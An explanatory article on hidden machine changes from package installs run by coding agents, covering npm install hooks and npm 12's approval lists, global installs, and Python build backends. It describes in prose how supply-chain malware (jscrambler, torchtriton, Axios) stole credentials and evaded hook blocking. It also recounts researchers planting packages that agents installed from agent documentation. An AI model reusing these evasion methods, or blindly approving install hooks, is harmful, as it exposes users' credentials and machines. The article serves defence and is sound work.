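# Hidden changes from package installs run by coding agents: install hooks, global installs, and how to record and reverse them

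## What happens when a coding agent installs a package

A coding agent is an AI system that carries out programming tasks by reading files, editing them and running commands. Many tasks need software that the computer does not have yet, so the agent installs it with a command such as `npm install better-sqlite3` or `pip install numpy`. A single command like this can create hundreds of directories, run other people's code, and change files unrelated to the project.

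Only some of these effects show up in the records that programmers check afterwards. Most of the unrecorded ones are harmless, but they still matter because people can't undo changes they don't know about.

### Packages, registries and lockfiles

A package is a bundle of code published for others to reuse, together with a file that describes it. Most packages are stored by name on a server called a registry, such as the npm registry for JavaScript or PyPI for Python. A package manager is a program that finds packages on a registry, downloads them and puts their files in place. The standard package manager for JavaScript is also called npm, and the one for Python is pip.

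A project lists the packages it needs in a manifest file, `package.json` for npm and often `requirements.txt` for Python. These are its direct dependencies, which *Towards a Benchmark for Dependency Decision-Making* (2026) describes as explicitly selected by the maintainers. Each of them needs further packages, which need others in turn. These are transitive dependencies, which nobody on the project picked by name. A modern JavaScript application can have hundreds or thousands of them, according to NodeSource's *Why Installing an npm Package Can Execute Code on Your Machine*. *Setup Complete, Now You Are Compromised* (Bagmar and Saraf, 2026) cites an earlier finding that anyone who installs an average npm package implicitly trusts 79 other packages and 39 maintainers.

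Manifests usually give version ranges rather than exact versions. The entry `^7.0.0` accepts any version 7, so the same manifest can lead to different software on different days. A lockfile removes this ambiguity by listing the exact versions chosen. Each entry in npm's lockfile holds the package's version, the address it came from, and a checksum, a short fingerprint computed from the archive's bytes, according to Debian's *package-lock.json* manual page. In its own *package-lock.json* documentation, npm tells projects to commit the file to version control, the system (nearly always Git) that stores a project's history. This is partly so that reviewers can see dependency changes in the diff, the line-by-line list of alterations.

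### The model, the harness and the shell tool

The two main parts of a coding agent are a language model, which only produces text, and a harness, which is the program around the model. Claude Code and Codex CLI are harnesses. *Do AI Coding Assistants Check Before They Install?* (Shan, 2026) describes how the harness passes the task to the model, runs the commands the model returns, and feeds their output back to it. Each request from the model to do something is a tool call, and the shell tool runs terminal commands, including installs.

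The harness also determines whether a person sees a command before it runs. According to Bagmar and Saraf, Claude Code shows a preview and waits for approval, while Copilot CLI and Codex CLI run commands immediately if the user starts either tool with its flags for automatic execution. An approval step shows the person only the command text, which for an install gives little indication of what the command will do.

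### One install, stage by stage

Suppose an agent runs `npm install better-sqlite3`, a database library, inside a project directory.

npm begins by choosing versions. The command gives none, so npm normally takes the release that the registry has tagged `latest`, then works out versions for everything that release needs. For packages already in the project, npm's manual gives a rule of precedence: if the lockfile's versions satisfy the manifest's ranges, npm uses them, and if the two conflict, the manifest wins and npm updates the lockfile. To do all this npm fetches package descriptions from the registry and keeps copies in a cache in the user's home directory. So the first writes outside the project happen before any package has arrived, though they are about as innocent as writes get.

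Next, npm downloads the archives into the same cache. Starting with version 12, npm's default settings block dependencies from Git repositories and block archives from web addresses whose host name differs from the registry's.

Then npm checks each archive against its checksum. A match means that the archive's contents are the ones recorded by the registry or the lockfile, but the code may still be faulty or malicious. The check itself changes no files outside the project.

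In a normal project install, npm then unpacks the files into `node_modules`, a directory inside the project. The `-g` flag requests a global install, which makes the package's programs available outside the current project. With this flag, npm unpacks the files outside the project and links the package's programs and manual pages into shared directories.

Next, npm may run code from the packages themselves. A package can supply install hooks, which are commands that the package manager runs automatically during installation. Hooks have legitimate uses. NodeSource lists `better-sqlite3` among the libraries that often have to compile C or C++ code for the particular machine, and other packages download a prebuilt program that suits it. But a hook runs as an ordinary process with the privileges of whoever started the install, so it can write wherever that user can. This is the only stage where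 the package's author, rather than npm's developers, determines what happens to the disk. npm 12 runs only the hooks that somebody has approved and skips the rest with a warning. In Python, pip can also run a package's code during an install, through its `setup.py` file.

Last, npm writes the lockfile, which stays in the project.

An install can make three kinds of changes outside the project. npm writes to its cache while choosing versions and downloading packages, a global install unpacks files outside the project by design, and an install hook can change anything the user has permission to change. Only the hook's changes can't be predicted from npm's manual.

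### Project, user and system scope

Scope is how far an install reaches. npm's *folders* documentation supplies an example path for each case:

- Project: `./node_modules`, which serves one project and disappears with its directory.
- User: `%AppData%\npm` on Windows, which serves one account on the machine.
- System: `/usr/local` on most Unix systems, which serves every account.

The user and system examples both come from `npm install -g`. This command installs packages under a directory called the prefix, and the default prefix depends on the operating system and on where Node.js, the program that runs JavaScript outside a browser, is installed. An agent that runs the same "global" install on two machines may therefore affect one account on the first and every account on the second.

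Scope also describes only where the package manager puts the package. A hook in a project-scope install can still edit a file in the home directory, and you couldn't tell from the command.

### Four tests for a hidden change

We can classify the effects of an install by whether they are visible in the text of the command, in the lockfile, in the project's version-control diff, and in the agent's own report of what it did.

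A hidden change is a lasting change that does not appear in the command, the lockfile or the diff. Temporary files that a hook creates and then deletes don't count. The definition leaves out the agent's report because the model writes it afterwards and can omit things or get them wrong. Shan scored agents from the logs of the containers they ran in, rather than from their own accounts, for much the same reason. Whether the agent disclosed the change in its report is a separate question.

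The three cases below show how the tests apply. The last one involves a shell profile, a file such as `~/.bashrc` whose commands run each time the user opens a terminal.

| Change | Command | Lockfile | Diff | Agent's report | Hidden? |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| A transitive dependency adds a line to the lockfile | No | Yes | Yes | Easy to include, since the agent can read the file | No |
| An install hook downloads a browser to a cache in the home directory | No | No | No | Unlikely, since npm does not display hook output by default | Yes |
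| An installer adds a line to a shell profile | No | No | No | Only if the installer printed a notice and the agent passed it on | Yes |

Small differences in how the agent works can change these answers. For example, if the agent adds `--no-save`, npm installs the package without updating the manifest or the lockfile, and most projects configure Git to ignore `node_modules`. The command still names the package the agent asked for, but the package's transitive dependencies no longer appear in any of the three records.

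The lockfile lists the library whose hook fetched the browser, but not the browser itself. If the hook requests the current version from a server, two people with identical lockfiles can end up with different browser versions. npm's documentation says that teammates with the same lockfile are "guaranteed to install exactly the same dependencies", which is fair for the package archives but not for files that hooks download.

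An agent may edit the shell profile itself, with a command that appends a line to `~/.bashrc`. The command text then shows the full change, though it's easy to overlook in a long session. An installer can make the same edit without it appearing in the command the agent ran.

### Hidden is not the same as malicious

Usually nobody hides these changes deliberately. The browser is in a cache so that several projects can share one copy, and the line in the shell profile lets the user run the new program by typing its name. Lockfiles and diffs don't record these changes because they are made outside the project.

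Signs of malice are often easy to see. Bagmar and Saraf mention `tdqm`, a PyPI package whose name swaps two letters of the popular `tqdm`. By their rough count from a GitHub search, over 960 `requirements.txt` files contain the name, where anyone who opened the file could see it.

An attack can also do damage without leaving a lasting change. In the torchtriton compromise, a package on the public index had the same name as an internal dependency of PyTorch, a machine-learning library. The package sent SSH keys (files that give access to other computers) and environment variables from the machines of people who ran the standard install. Copying a key doesn't alter it, so a complete list of altered files could miss the theft, and restoring every file would not undo it. Recording and reversing changes is worth doing for other reasons, but it is a poor substitute for not running the code.

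### What an agent changes

A developer who types `npm install` sets off the same stages, but an agent's installs differ in how routinely they happen, what the installing process can access, and who is paying attention.

Coding agents run many shell commands. In *SWE-chat*, Baumann, Padmakumar and colleagues (2026) collected almost 18,000 sessions volunteered by open-source developers, and more than 45% of the roughly 2 million tool calls were shell commands. In *AgentLogs*, Richards, Horikawa and colleagues (2026) found that shell interaction made up 37.4% of 28.5 million calls by agents on GitHub's cloud platform. It is harder to say how many of these were installs. In SWE-chat, 5.9% of calls used build tools, a category that includes npm, pnpm, uv and cargo. All four can install packages, but the category also includes commands that only run a Python script or compile a program. Installing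 is at least common enough that *On Turn-Level Best-of-N Sampling for Scaling LLM Agents* (2026) lists it as a separate category of agent behavior, alongside editing a file and running a test. Agents also sometimes run installs the user didn't ask for. In one SWE-chat session, the user wanted a README file updated, and the agent ran installation commands until the user interrupted and repeated the request.

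The install runs with whatever access the agent has. Bagmar and Saraf note that on a developer's own computer, this means the developer's permissions and environment, which often include passwords and access keys for other services. Hidden changes are mostly a problem for agents that work on a machine someone intends to keep. On GitHub's platform, each cloud agent session gets a fresh sandbox, so a cached browser or a line added to a shell profile disappears when the session ends.

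Schneier (2026), in *AI Coding Agents Are Installing Unknown/Untrusted Code on Corporate Networks*, describes an experiment by researchers at an Israeli startup. They looked at the documentation files that companies publish for AI agents and found 120 that pointed to unregistered packages or domain names. They registered a handful of these and published packages that only contacted the researchers' server. The first contact came within an hour, from a Fortune 500 company, and a few dozen followed. Records of which process had started each install showed that the agents Claude, Codex and Hermes were involved.

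By default, npm hides the output of dependencies' install hooks, so a developer running `npm install` is probably less likely to notice a suspicious hook than Nesbitt, who writes about package management, suggests. Nesbitt argues that a developer might spot one in the terminal, while an agent busy fixing a build won't. A developer does see the command itself, and may notice an odd name or an unfamiliar address in the short pause before pressing Enter. An agent with automatic approval removes that pause, which Bagmar and Saraf think is what has kept unchecked installs survivable so far.

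People can check an agent's work afterwards, but they usually look at the pull request, the proposed change that the agent submits for review. Richards and colleagues point out that it shows the diff but not the commands, which are only in the agent's log. It is unclear whether reviewers open the log. *Large-Scale Study of GitHub Copilot Trajectories* (Sohail, Kurmantayev and colleagues, 2026) examined 7,581 pull requests by GitHub's Copilot agent. In 58% of them, no human commented to ask the agent for more work, and developers merged 62% of those. Some developers may have read the whole log and had no objections, so these figures are only indirect evidence about supervision. They also come from cloud sandboxes, where an unnoticed change to the machine does little harm, and may not carry over to agents on people's own computers.

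## npm install hooks and the switch to opt-in

For most of npm's history, installing a package automatically ran its install hooks. Since npm 12, released on July 8, 2026, hooks in dependencies run by default only after they are approved. Three days after that release, an attacker published a version of jscrambler, an established npm package, with a hook that launched a password-stealing program. npm 12 would have skipped the hook, but many people were still using older versions of npm. Within three hours, the attacker had switched to a method that the new default doesn't cover.

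### The hooks and their order

A package declares its hooks in the `scripts` field of its `package.json`, where each entry pairs a name with a shell command. Most install hooks are named `preinstall`, `install` or `postinstall`. npm runs them in that order, for both direct and transitive dependencies.

According to npm's *scripts* documentation, all three hooks, including `preinstall`, run after npm has put the package's files into `node_modules`. Semgrep's *RIP post/preinstall scripts* (2026) instead describes `preinstall` as running before the files arrive, as its name suggests. But jscrambler's `preinstall` hook ran a file from inside the package, so it couldn't have worked unless the files were already there. The project's own `preinstall` is an exception as of version 12, when npm's changelog lists a change that makes it run before npm puts files into `node_modules`.

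A fourth hook, `prepare`, builds a package from its source, for example by translating TypeScript into JavaScript. Authors normally run it before publishing, so npm doesn't run it for packages from the registry. npm does run it for the project itself when someone types `npm install` without naming a package, and for dependencies that come from a Git repository. To build a Git dependency, npm first installs that dependency's own development tools, so one Git dependency can bring in a second set of packages.

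npm runs an install hook for some packages that don't declare one. If a package contains a `binding.gyp` file, which holds build instructions for C or C++ code, and has no `preinstall` or `install` command, npm runs `node-gyp rebuild` to compile the code. According to *Make install scripts opt-in*, the proposal that led to npm 12's new default, the lockfile's marker for packages with install hooks is false for these packages. Gooding (2026), in *npm v12 Ships With Install Scripts Off by Default*, describes attacks in which a small `binding.gyp` file ran malicious code during installation and got past scanners that only read the `scripts` field.

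### What a hook can reach

A hook starts in its own package's folder. The environment variable `INIT_CWD` holds the directory where the user ran npm, so the hook can find the surrounding project. npm also gives the hook the package's name, version, download address and checksum. It passes the hook's command to the system's shell, which can start any program.

When root, the administrator account, runs `npm install`, it is unclear whether hooks keep root's full privileges. npm's documentation used to say that they would run as the owner of the working directory, but a 2026 changelog entry lists the removal of this passage and describes the behavior as obsolete. It is safer to assume that hooks run as root under `sudo npm install`.

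Since version 7, npm has hidden hooks' output unless the user adds the `--foreground-scripts` flag. A hook that exits with an error normally aborts the install, so an agent tends to learn about hooks only when they fail. Version 7 also dropped uninstall hooks, so a package can't run its own cleanup script when npm removes it.

### Why packages have hooks, and how many do

The main legitimate use of install hooks is compiling code, as `better-sqlite3` does. Puppeteer, Playwright, Cypress and Electron use them to download large programs, mostly browsers, that would be awkward to keep in the registry. Semgrep also lists setup tasks, such as generating configuration files or patching other dependencies.

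npm's own documentation takes a stricter view and accepts `preinstall` and `install` hooks only for compiling on the target machine. Even that need is shrinking. Many authors now publish a ready-built package for each operating system and let npm pick the right one, as the build tool esbuild does with packages such as `@esbuild/linux-x64`. This needs no hook, and the binary gets a version and a checksum in the lockfile.

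The figure usually cited is that 2.2% of npm packages have install hooks. In *What are Weak Links in the npm Supply Chain?*, Zahan, Zimmermann and colleagues (2021) downloaded the descriptions of 1.63 million npm packages in June 2021, discarded about 136,000 unusable ones, and found install scripts in the latest version of 33,249 of the remaining packages. Guo, Liu and colleagues (2026) still cite the figure in *How Effective Are NPM Malicious Package Detectors?*, although they put the registry at over 3.57 million packages. *Make install scripts opt-in* lists an up-to-date count for the most-downloaded packages as an open question.

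A small share of packages can affect most installs. If 2.2% of packages have hooks, an install that adds 80 random packages has about an 83% chance of including at least one hook. Real dependencies aren't chosen at random, so this is only a rough guide, but it explains why hooks feel common to people who rarely publish packages with them.

### What npm 12 turned off

GitHub's *npm install-time security and GAT bypass2fa deprecation* (2026) announced the release. GitHub owns npm. Three things that `npm install` used to do automatically now need permission:

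- **Running dependencies' hooks.** npm skips `preinstall`, `install` and `postinstall`, along with the implicit `node-gyp` build. It also skips `prepare` for dependencies from Git repositories, local files and links.
- **Fetching dependencies from Git.** The `--allow-git` setting now defaults to `none`, for direct and transitive dependencies.
- **Fetching archives from other web addresses.** The `--allow-remote` setting also defaults to `none`. Archives from the registry still work.

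The settings for local files and directories keep their old defaults, as GitHub (2026) explained when it previewed the changes in June.

The restriction on Git closes a hole that remained even when users turned hooks off. npm fetches a Git dependency by running the `git` program, but the dependency can include an `.npmrc` settings file that changes where npm looks for `git`. A malicious repository could therefore make npm run a different program. The older `--ignore-scripts` flag didn't prevent this because it turns off hooks, not npm's ordinary calls to Git. GitHub's *npm bulk trusted publishing config and script security now generally available* gave this as the reason for adding `--allow-git` to npm 11.10, where users still had to turn it on.

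When npm 12 skips a hook, the install still succeeds, and npm lists the affected packages at the end. Gooding notes that if the skipped hook would have compiled a module, the program crashes later, when it tries to load that module. A stricter setting, `strict-allow-scripts`, makes the install fail instead and is meant mainly for automated builds.

### The `allowScripts` field

A project approves hooks in a field of its `package.json`:

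```json
"allowScripts": {
  "sqlite3@5.1.7": true,
  "core-js": false
}
```

With this field, npm runs the hooks of `sqlite3` at version 5.1.7, silently skips those of `core-js`, and skips those of all other packages with a warning. A denial means that somebody has reviewed the package and decided against its hooks, while packages without an entry haven't been reviewed yet.

People normally maintain the field with `npm install-scripts approve` and `npm install-scripts deny`. By default, an approval covers only the installed version. When `sqlite3` moves to another version, the entry no longer matches and npm skips the hook until someone approves that version. An entry can list several exact versions but not a range such as "anything below 6", because a range would approve releases that nobody has seen. A denial covers every version of the package. Running `npm install-scripts approve --all`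 approves every unreviewed hook at once but doesn't override denials. Approving a package doesn't immediately run its hooks, so the user runs `npm rebuild` to do that.

Package names can be misleading, so npm compares approvals with the identity its own resolver recorded and ignores the name inside the archive. A package's author can write any name in its internal `package.json`, and the registry doesn't check it against the published name. A project can also install one package under another's name. npm ignores any `allowScripts` field in a dependency too, so a package can't approve itself.

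Because the field is in a committed file, reviewers can see in the diff that a hook has permission to run, but not what it does to the machine.

### Global installs and npx

Global installs have no project `package.json` to hold approvals, and neither does npx, a command that downloads a package and runs its program in one step. According to npm's documentation, the user can instead name packages for a single command, as in `npm install -g --allow-scripts=canvas,sharp`, or save the same list with `npm config set allow-scripts=canvas,sharp --location=user`.

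The second option writes to the user's own `.npmrc` file, so the approval also applies outside the project. The text of the `config` command shows the change, but the lockfile and the diff don't. Weeks later, `npm install -g sharp` could run a hook, and nothing in that command would show why. The saved list is also less precise than the project field. *Make install scripts opt-in* says the list can't express the full combination of denials and version pins, so in the documented form an approval for `canvas` covers any later version, whether its maintainers or someone with their password published it.

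An agent trying to get a tool working has little reason to use the one-time flag instead of the saved setting, which fixes the same error and keeps it from coming back.

### pnpm, Yarn and Bun

npm was late to this. *Make install scripts opt-in* calls it the last major JavaScript package manager to run every hook by default, and compares it with its competitors:

| Package manager | What it does with dependencies' hooks | Where a project keeps approvals |
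|---|---|---|
| npm 12 | Skips them with a warning unless the project approves them | `allowScripts` in `package.json` |
| pnpm 10 and later | Blocks them unless the project approves them | `allowBuilds` in `pnpm-workspace.yaml` |
| Yarn Berry, the newer line of Yarn | Blocks them unless the project opts in | `dependenciesMeta` in `package.json` |
| Bun | Blocks them, except for about 400 packages on a built-in list | `trustedDependencies` in `package.json` |

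The entry for Yarn needs caution because Semgrep describes the block only for Plug'n'Play, a mode in which Yarn doesn't create a `node_modules` directory. The `enableScripts` setting in a project's `.yarnrc.yml` is more reliable than either description.

Bun's built-in list saves users from approving popular packages one by one. But an attacker who takes over any of those packages can run a hook on Bun users' machines without anyone's approval. pnpm is stricter. Besides blocking hooks, version 11 by default won't install a release until it is 24 hours old, according to Gooding.

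### Where npm still runs hooks

npm 12 always runs the project's own hooks, on the grounds that the developer controls them. That is reasonable for a project the developer wrote, but less so for a repository that an agent cloned a minute ago to try out. Typing `npm install` there runs the repository's own `preinstall`, `postinstall` and `prepare` commands. The repository also comes with its own `allowScripts` field, so its author's approvals take effect on the agent's machine. The `--ignore-scripts` flag turns off both kinds of hook, which makes it the better choice for an unfamiliar repository.

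The new default also doesn't protect people who haven't upgraded. According to npm's documentation for version 11, the `allowScripts` field is advisory in that version, so npm lists unreviewed hooks but still runs them. Node.js comes with a copy of npm, and ApostropheCMS, which makes a web publishing system, notes in its upgrade guide that releases up to Node.js 26 come with npm 11. In July 2026 the npm team hoped to bring version 12 to Node.js 24 and 26, but the decision was up to the Node.js release team. Linux distributions can be further behind. Debian's *npm-rebuild* manual page lists npm 9.2.0 for the trixie release, and that version has no approval list.

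An agent usually uses whichever npm version is already installed, so the same command can run a hook on one machine and skip it on another. For this reason, the output of `npm --version` is worth recording with the install.

### The jscrambler attack

jscrambler is the command-line client for a commercial service that makes JavaScript code harder to read and copy. It had about 15,800 downloads a week, according to Socket's *jscrambler npm Package Compromised in Supply Chain Attack* (2026). On July 11, 2026, an attacker with a stolen publishing token released version 8.14.0. Prabhu (2026), in *jscrambler npm package publishes malicious preinstall binary*, compared it with the previous release. The archive had grown from 37.8 kB to 7.9 MB, and `package.json` contained a `preinstall` hook that no earlier version had.

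The hook ran a short script, `setup.js`, which chose one of three programs depending on the operating system and copied it to a randomly named hidden file in the temporary directory. The script then started the program as a separate process, which kept running after npm finished. The program collected browser passwords, cloud credentials and cryptocurrency wallets. Socket also found that it searched for Claude Desktop, Cursor and other AI tool settings, which often contain access keys.

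*IronWorm Returns as jscrambler, Rustier Than Ever* (Satou, 2026) describes what the program left behind. On Linux, it tried to install itself as a system service and fell back on a user service or a scheduled job. On macOS, it used the files that start programs at login, and on Windows, it copied itself into the Startup folder. None of this appears in a lockfile or a project diff, and deleting `node_modules` doesn't remove it.

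Socket wrote that installing jscrambler 8.14.0 was enough to trigger the program. That was true for npm 11 and earlier, but npm 12 would have skipped the hook by default. No earlier version of jscrambler had needed an install hook, so projects had no reason to approve the package, and an approval pinned to an earlier version would not have covered the new release. The hook could therefore still harm people who used an older npm or had set npm 12 to allow every hook. None of the analyses reports how many victims were in either group.

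Upgrading to npm 12 would not have been enough for long, because the attacker kept changing the method. SafeDep's *Official jscrambler npm Package Compromised Across Multiple Releases* (2026) traces the sequence:

| Version | Published on July 11 (UTC) | What started the program |
|---|---|---|
| 8.14.0 | 15:12 | `preinstall` hook |
| 8.16.0 | 17:26 | `preinstall` hook |
| 8.17.0 | 17:41 | `preinstall` hook, plus an `allowScripts` entry |
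| 8.18.0 | 17:46 | Importing the package or running its command |
| 8.20.0 | 17:53 | Importing the package or running its command |

In jscrambler 8.17.0, the attacker added an `allowScripts` entry for jscrambler to the package's own `package.json`. SafeDep interprets this as an attempt to get around pnpm's restrictions, but `allowScripts` is an npm field, and pnpm uses `allowBuilds`. The entry wouldn't have worked on npm 12 either, because npm ignores the field in a dependency's `package.json`.

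Five minutes later the attacker stopped using hooks and, in version 8.18.0, put the same malicious code at the top of the package's main file and its command-line program. The code ran as soon as another program imported jscrambler or someone used the command. No install-hook setting, including `--ignore-scripts`, prevents that, and a scanner that looked only for hooks would have reported the package as clean.

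*Security Incident Postmortem* (Fortuna, 2026) explains that the stolen token belonged to Jscrambler's own release process. Staff noticed the first release within seconds but revoked a different credential, so the attacker could keep publishing. Fortuna counts 1,614 downloads across the affected packages, compared with about 391 of jscrambler on a typical Saturday. Fortuna suspects most came from security researchers and says no customer reported any harm. This is plausible given how briefly the versions were available, although people don't always notice when someone has copied their passwords.

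Another attacker also ran code on import that week, in malicious releases of four AsyncAPI packages that Microsoft (2026) identified on July 14. Two cases don't establish a trend, but they do show that the change takes little work. In jscrambler's case, the attacker left the malicious program unchanged and only moved the few lines that started it.

A waiting period would have helped against both versions of the jscrambler attack, because Jscrambler's developers had replaced every malicious release with a clean one by the end of the day. Fortuna recommends npm's `min-release-age` setting, which holds back new releases for a chosen number of days.

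### Are approval lists worth the trouble?

People who object to blocking hooks often say that developers install packages in order to run them, so malicious code will run anyway. This objection partly holds for coding agents. An agent often runs tests that import a package within minutes of installing it, and the import runs with the same access the hook would have had.

*Make install scripts opt-in* replies that plenty of installed code never runs. A build server may install hundreds of packages just to bundle them, and someone who mistypes a package name may notice before importing anything. In the March 2026 attack on Axios, a very popular library, the attackers added a dependency that Axios never imported and that existed only for its `postinstall` hook. According to Semgrep, the hook downloaded a remote-control program, deleted itself, and replaced the package's `package.json` with a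 clean copy. With hooks blocked, none of that dependency's code would have run.

Gooding says that almost every worm and credential stealer on npm since late 2025 ran at install time. That supports blocking hooks, but those attackers had no reason to try anything else. As more people move to npm 12, the share of attacks that an approval list stops will probably fall. Forcing attackers to rely on code that runs on import would still be useful, because runtime restrictions and code review have some chance of catching it.

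The other worry is that approval becomes a habit. Version pins make this more likely, because each update of a package with a hook needs another approval. There is also little to review. npm shows which packages have hooks and the command each one runs, but Gooding points out that it doesn't show whether the command reads passwords, contacts a server or writes outside the package. The command `node install.js` looks the same in a safe package and a malicious one. A contributor has proposed a report that would flag these actions and show whether the hook has changed since it was last approved.

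Agents could get into the habit of approving every hook faster than people do, though this is a prediction, not a documented incident. Suppose an agent installs `better-sqlite3` with npm 12, and the tests fail because the module wasn't compiled. npm's warning lists several packages with skipped hooks. The agent could approve only `better-sqlite3`, but running `npm install-scripts approve --all` and then `npm rebuild` would also approve and build it. The tests would pass either way, so nothing in the task would discourage the agent from approving everything. The new entries would appear in the diff, but the hooks would have run before anyone reviewed it.

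Even careless approval with `--all` leaves some protection if the approvals are pinned, because it covers only the packages and versions installed at that moment. If a harmless package later gains a malicious hook, as jscrambler did, npm will skip the hook. The package never needed one, so it will keep working and the agent will have no error to fix. But if a different package breaks at the same time, the agent may run `--all` again and approve the malicious hook along with the one it wanted. Approving the broken package by name avoids this and takes no more effort.

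## Code that runs when Python packages are built, installed and started

Python packages have no equivalent of npm's `postinstall` command, and most pip installs only unpack files. But if pip has to build a package from source, it runs build code that the package's author chose, without the prior approval that npm 12 requires. A package can also install a start-up file, which may run code every time Python starts.

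### Source distributions and wheels

A release on PyPI can come in two forms. A source distribution is an archive, typically a `.tar.gz` file, of the project's source code and some metadata. A wheel is a `.whl` file whose contents are ready to use, according to *Building distributions* by Astral, which develops the newer Python package manager uv. pip installs a wheel by unpacking it into `site-packages`, the directory where a Python environment keeps its packages. None of the wheel's code should run during installation, but a flaw in versions before pip 26.1, CVE-2026-6357, could allow it to. InfoQ (2026) lists the fix among the security patches in pip 26.1.

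pip can't install a source distribution directly. It first has to turn the source into a wheel, and that means running code.

Pip usually chooses between the two forms itself. For a given version, it uses a wheel if one fits the computer and otherwise falls back on the source. *Preventing unwanted attempts to build sdists*, a thread on Python's packaging forum ("sdist" is short for source distribution), lists several reasons for the fallback. The project may not publish wheels for the user's platform or Python version, or pip may be too old to recognize the right one. The user may also run the install after the author has uploaded the source but before the wheels are uploaded. So the same `pip install` command can unpack files on one machine and run a build on another.

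### A source install, step by step

Smith and Kluyver (2015), in *PEP 517*, defined the modern build procedure. (A PEP, or Python Enhancement Proposal, is a design document for a change to Python or its tools.) It relies on a file called `pyproject.toml`, which names the build backend and lists the packages needed to run it:

```toml
[build-system]
requires = ["hatchling"]
build-backend = "hatchling.build"
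```

The backend is the program that turns the source into a wheel. Here it is Hatchling, a common choice. pip's *Build System Interface* documentation describes the steps:

| What pip does | Package-supplied code that can run |
|---|---|
| Reads `pyproject.toml` | None |
| Creates a temporary build environment | None |
| Installs the packages under `requires` | Their build code, if they also come as source |
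| Calls `get_requires_for_build_wheel`, if the backend has it, and installs any extra packages it returns | The backend and the package's build scripts |
| Calls `prepare_metadata_for_build_wheel`, if the backend has it, to get the name, version and dependencies | The backend and the package's build scripts |
| Calls `build_wheel` to make the wheel | The backend and the package's build scripts |
| Unpacks the wheel into `site-packages` | None |

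The package's author controls most of this. A package can contain its own backend, which it declares with the `backend-path` setting. Smith and Kluyver included this setting for backends that build themselves and for projects that wrap a standard backend in custom code.

The author also picks the build requirements, which can be version ranges or the address of a Git repository. Users who pin their project's own dependencies can still get different build tools from one day to the next. Ordinary constraints files limit the versions pip may choose. They stopped applying to build environments in pip 26.2, according to *Announcement* (2026) from the Python Packaging Authority (PyPA), which maintains pip. Users now need a separate `--build-constraint` option to limit build tool versions.

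Pip can cache the wheel it builds and reuse it, so a second install of the same version may run no build code. Someone who repeats an agent's install to find out what it did may therefore miss what the build code did the first time, unless they clear the cache first.

### Builds that only look up metadata

pip needs to know a package's dependencies before it can work out what else to install. For a source distribution, it usually gets them from the backend. If the backend has no separate metadata function, pip builds the entire wheel just to read them. A package's code can therefore run even if pip never installs the package.

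pip can run a package's code even when told only to download it, as Knechtel (2025) shows in *Python packaging* with pip 25.0. Knechtel made a source distribution whose backend was a single line that printed a message and quit, then ran `pip download` on it with dependencies turned off. The archive was already on the disk, and its name and version were in the file name, the directory name and two metadata files. pip still ran the backend to check that the name and version matched the request. `pip install --dry-run` also runs the backend, since it skips only copying the files into the environment.

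Brendan Dolan-Gavitt, a security researcher, had discovered this by accident a few years earlier. To find out which packages on PyPI depended on certain others, Dolan-Gavitt started a dry-run install of all 397,267. Many had wheels, so far fewer had to be built, but the builds that ran left two anime pictures in the home directory, and a package that Dolan-Gavitt never identified tried to run `sudo`. Dolan-Gavitt attributed much of this to poor `setup.py` practices. The case shows that packages can make hidden changes without malice, even during a dry run.

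Since version 25.3, pip can skip the full download in a dry run when the index supplies a package's metadata separately. According to its documentation, though, pip still calls the build backend when a source distribution's metadata isn't otherwise available.

By default, uv also builds source distributions while it works out versions, according to the commit message for uv's *Add `--no-build`*. Updating a lockfile can therefore run package code even if nobody installs anything. A newer tool, nab, is stricter by default. According to its *Build policy*, it reads remote source distributions without running them and calls build backends only for local projects. However, a repository that an agent has just cloned from somebody else counts as local, so nab can still run its build code.

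An agent trying to be careful could easily run `pip download` to inspect a package, which would execute the code it meant to read. Knechtel recommends downloading the archive from PyPI's website or its JSON interface instead.

### Build isolation is not a sandbox

pip calls its build environment "isolated", which sounds like a security feature. Smith and Kluyver had other reasons for recommending it. If one package needs version 1.8.1 of a build tool and another needs 1.7.2, a single environment can't hold both, and replacing the version a user already has would be "rather rude". Isolation also exposes packages that build only on their author's computer because the author forgot to list a requirement.

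Build isolation changes which Python modules the backend can import, but it doesn't restrict access to files or the network. The backend runs with the permissions of whoever ran pip, so it can read SSH keys, edit a shell profile or contact a server. As the Python Developer Tooling Handbook's *Why Installing a Python Package Can Run Code* puts it, "Isolation is not sandboxing". pip 26.2 added an experimental option to build in standard virtual environments, which are directories with their own sets of Python packages. This option separates packages more reliably but doesn't limit the backend's access to the machine.

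Knechtel notes that pip doesn't drop administrator rights before building a package, so `sudo pip install` can run a stranger's build code as root.

Even builds that follow PEP 517 can leave files behind. The standard allows backends to store intermediate files in caches, which may be outside the project.

### `setup.py` and build plug-ins

Older packages have no `[build-system]` table in `pyproject.toml`, or no `pyproject.toml` at all. For these, pip falls back on setuptools, the traditional backend, in a compatibility mode that runs the package's `setup.py`, an ordinary Python program that can do anything the user can. Before version 25.3, pip ran `setup.py` directly in some cases, but it now runs the script only through the backend. According to Astral, uv also builds dependencies that don't declare a build system.

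At the PyTexas conference in 2026, Christopher Ariza reported that 454 of the top 1,000 PyPI packages still included a `setup.py`. The Python Developer Tooling Handbook cites this as evidence that install-time code is a current problem, but the number probably overstates it, because pip doesn't run `setup.py` when it installs a wheel, and the count doesn't show how many of the 454 packages have no wheel.

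A package without `setup.py` can still run code when it is built, because many build backends accept plug-ins. Veracode's *Modern Python Build Hooks* describes an experiment with a renamed copy of certifi, a widely used Python package. The experimenter turned on Hatchling's custom plug-in with one line in `pyproject.toml` and added a short file, `hatch_build.py`, that wrote a text file to the temporary directory. pip reported a normal, successful install, and the text file was there afterwards. The same method worked with PDM, another packaging tool. It also worked with Poetry, through an undocumented feature that ran Python code from a file called `BUILD.md`, which looks like documentation.

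Someone who checks a package only for `setup.py` would miss all of these. The npm attacks that used `binding.gyp` to avoid notice exploited the same habit of checking only the best-known place.

pip's output during the Veracode experiment contained only its usual progress messages, such as "Building wheel". Harmless packages produce them too. An agent's log can therefore show that a build took place, which is useful, but usually not what the build did.

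### Installing only wheels

Both pip and uv can refuse source distributions. pip's *Secure installs* guide recommends `--only-binary :all:` together with `--require-hashes`, which makes pip check every package against a checksum in the project's requirements file. uv's equivalent of `--only-binary :all:` is `--no-build`. With this option on, uv runs no arbitrary Python code while working out versions, according to its reference on Docs.rs, and any operation that needs a build ends in an error. uv still reuses wheels it built earlier, so a package whose build code has already run can still be installed with the option on.

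These options stop build code from running during downloads, dry runs and installs, but they don't stop code that runs when a program imports the package or when Python starts. Wheels with compiled code are also harder to inspect. Knechtel points out that even if such a wheel includes C source files, the user can't confirm that the compiled program came from them. The source distribution may be better for someone who will read the code. Few agents' installs get that review, and for the rest, skipping the build removes one chance for unknown code to run.

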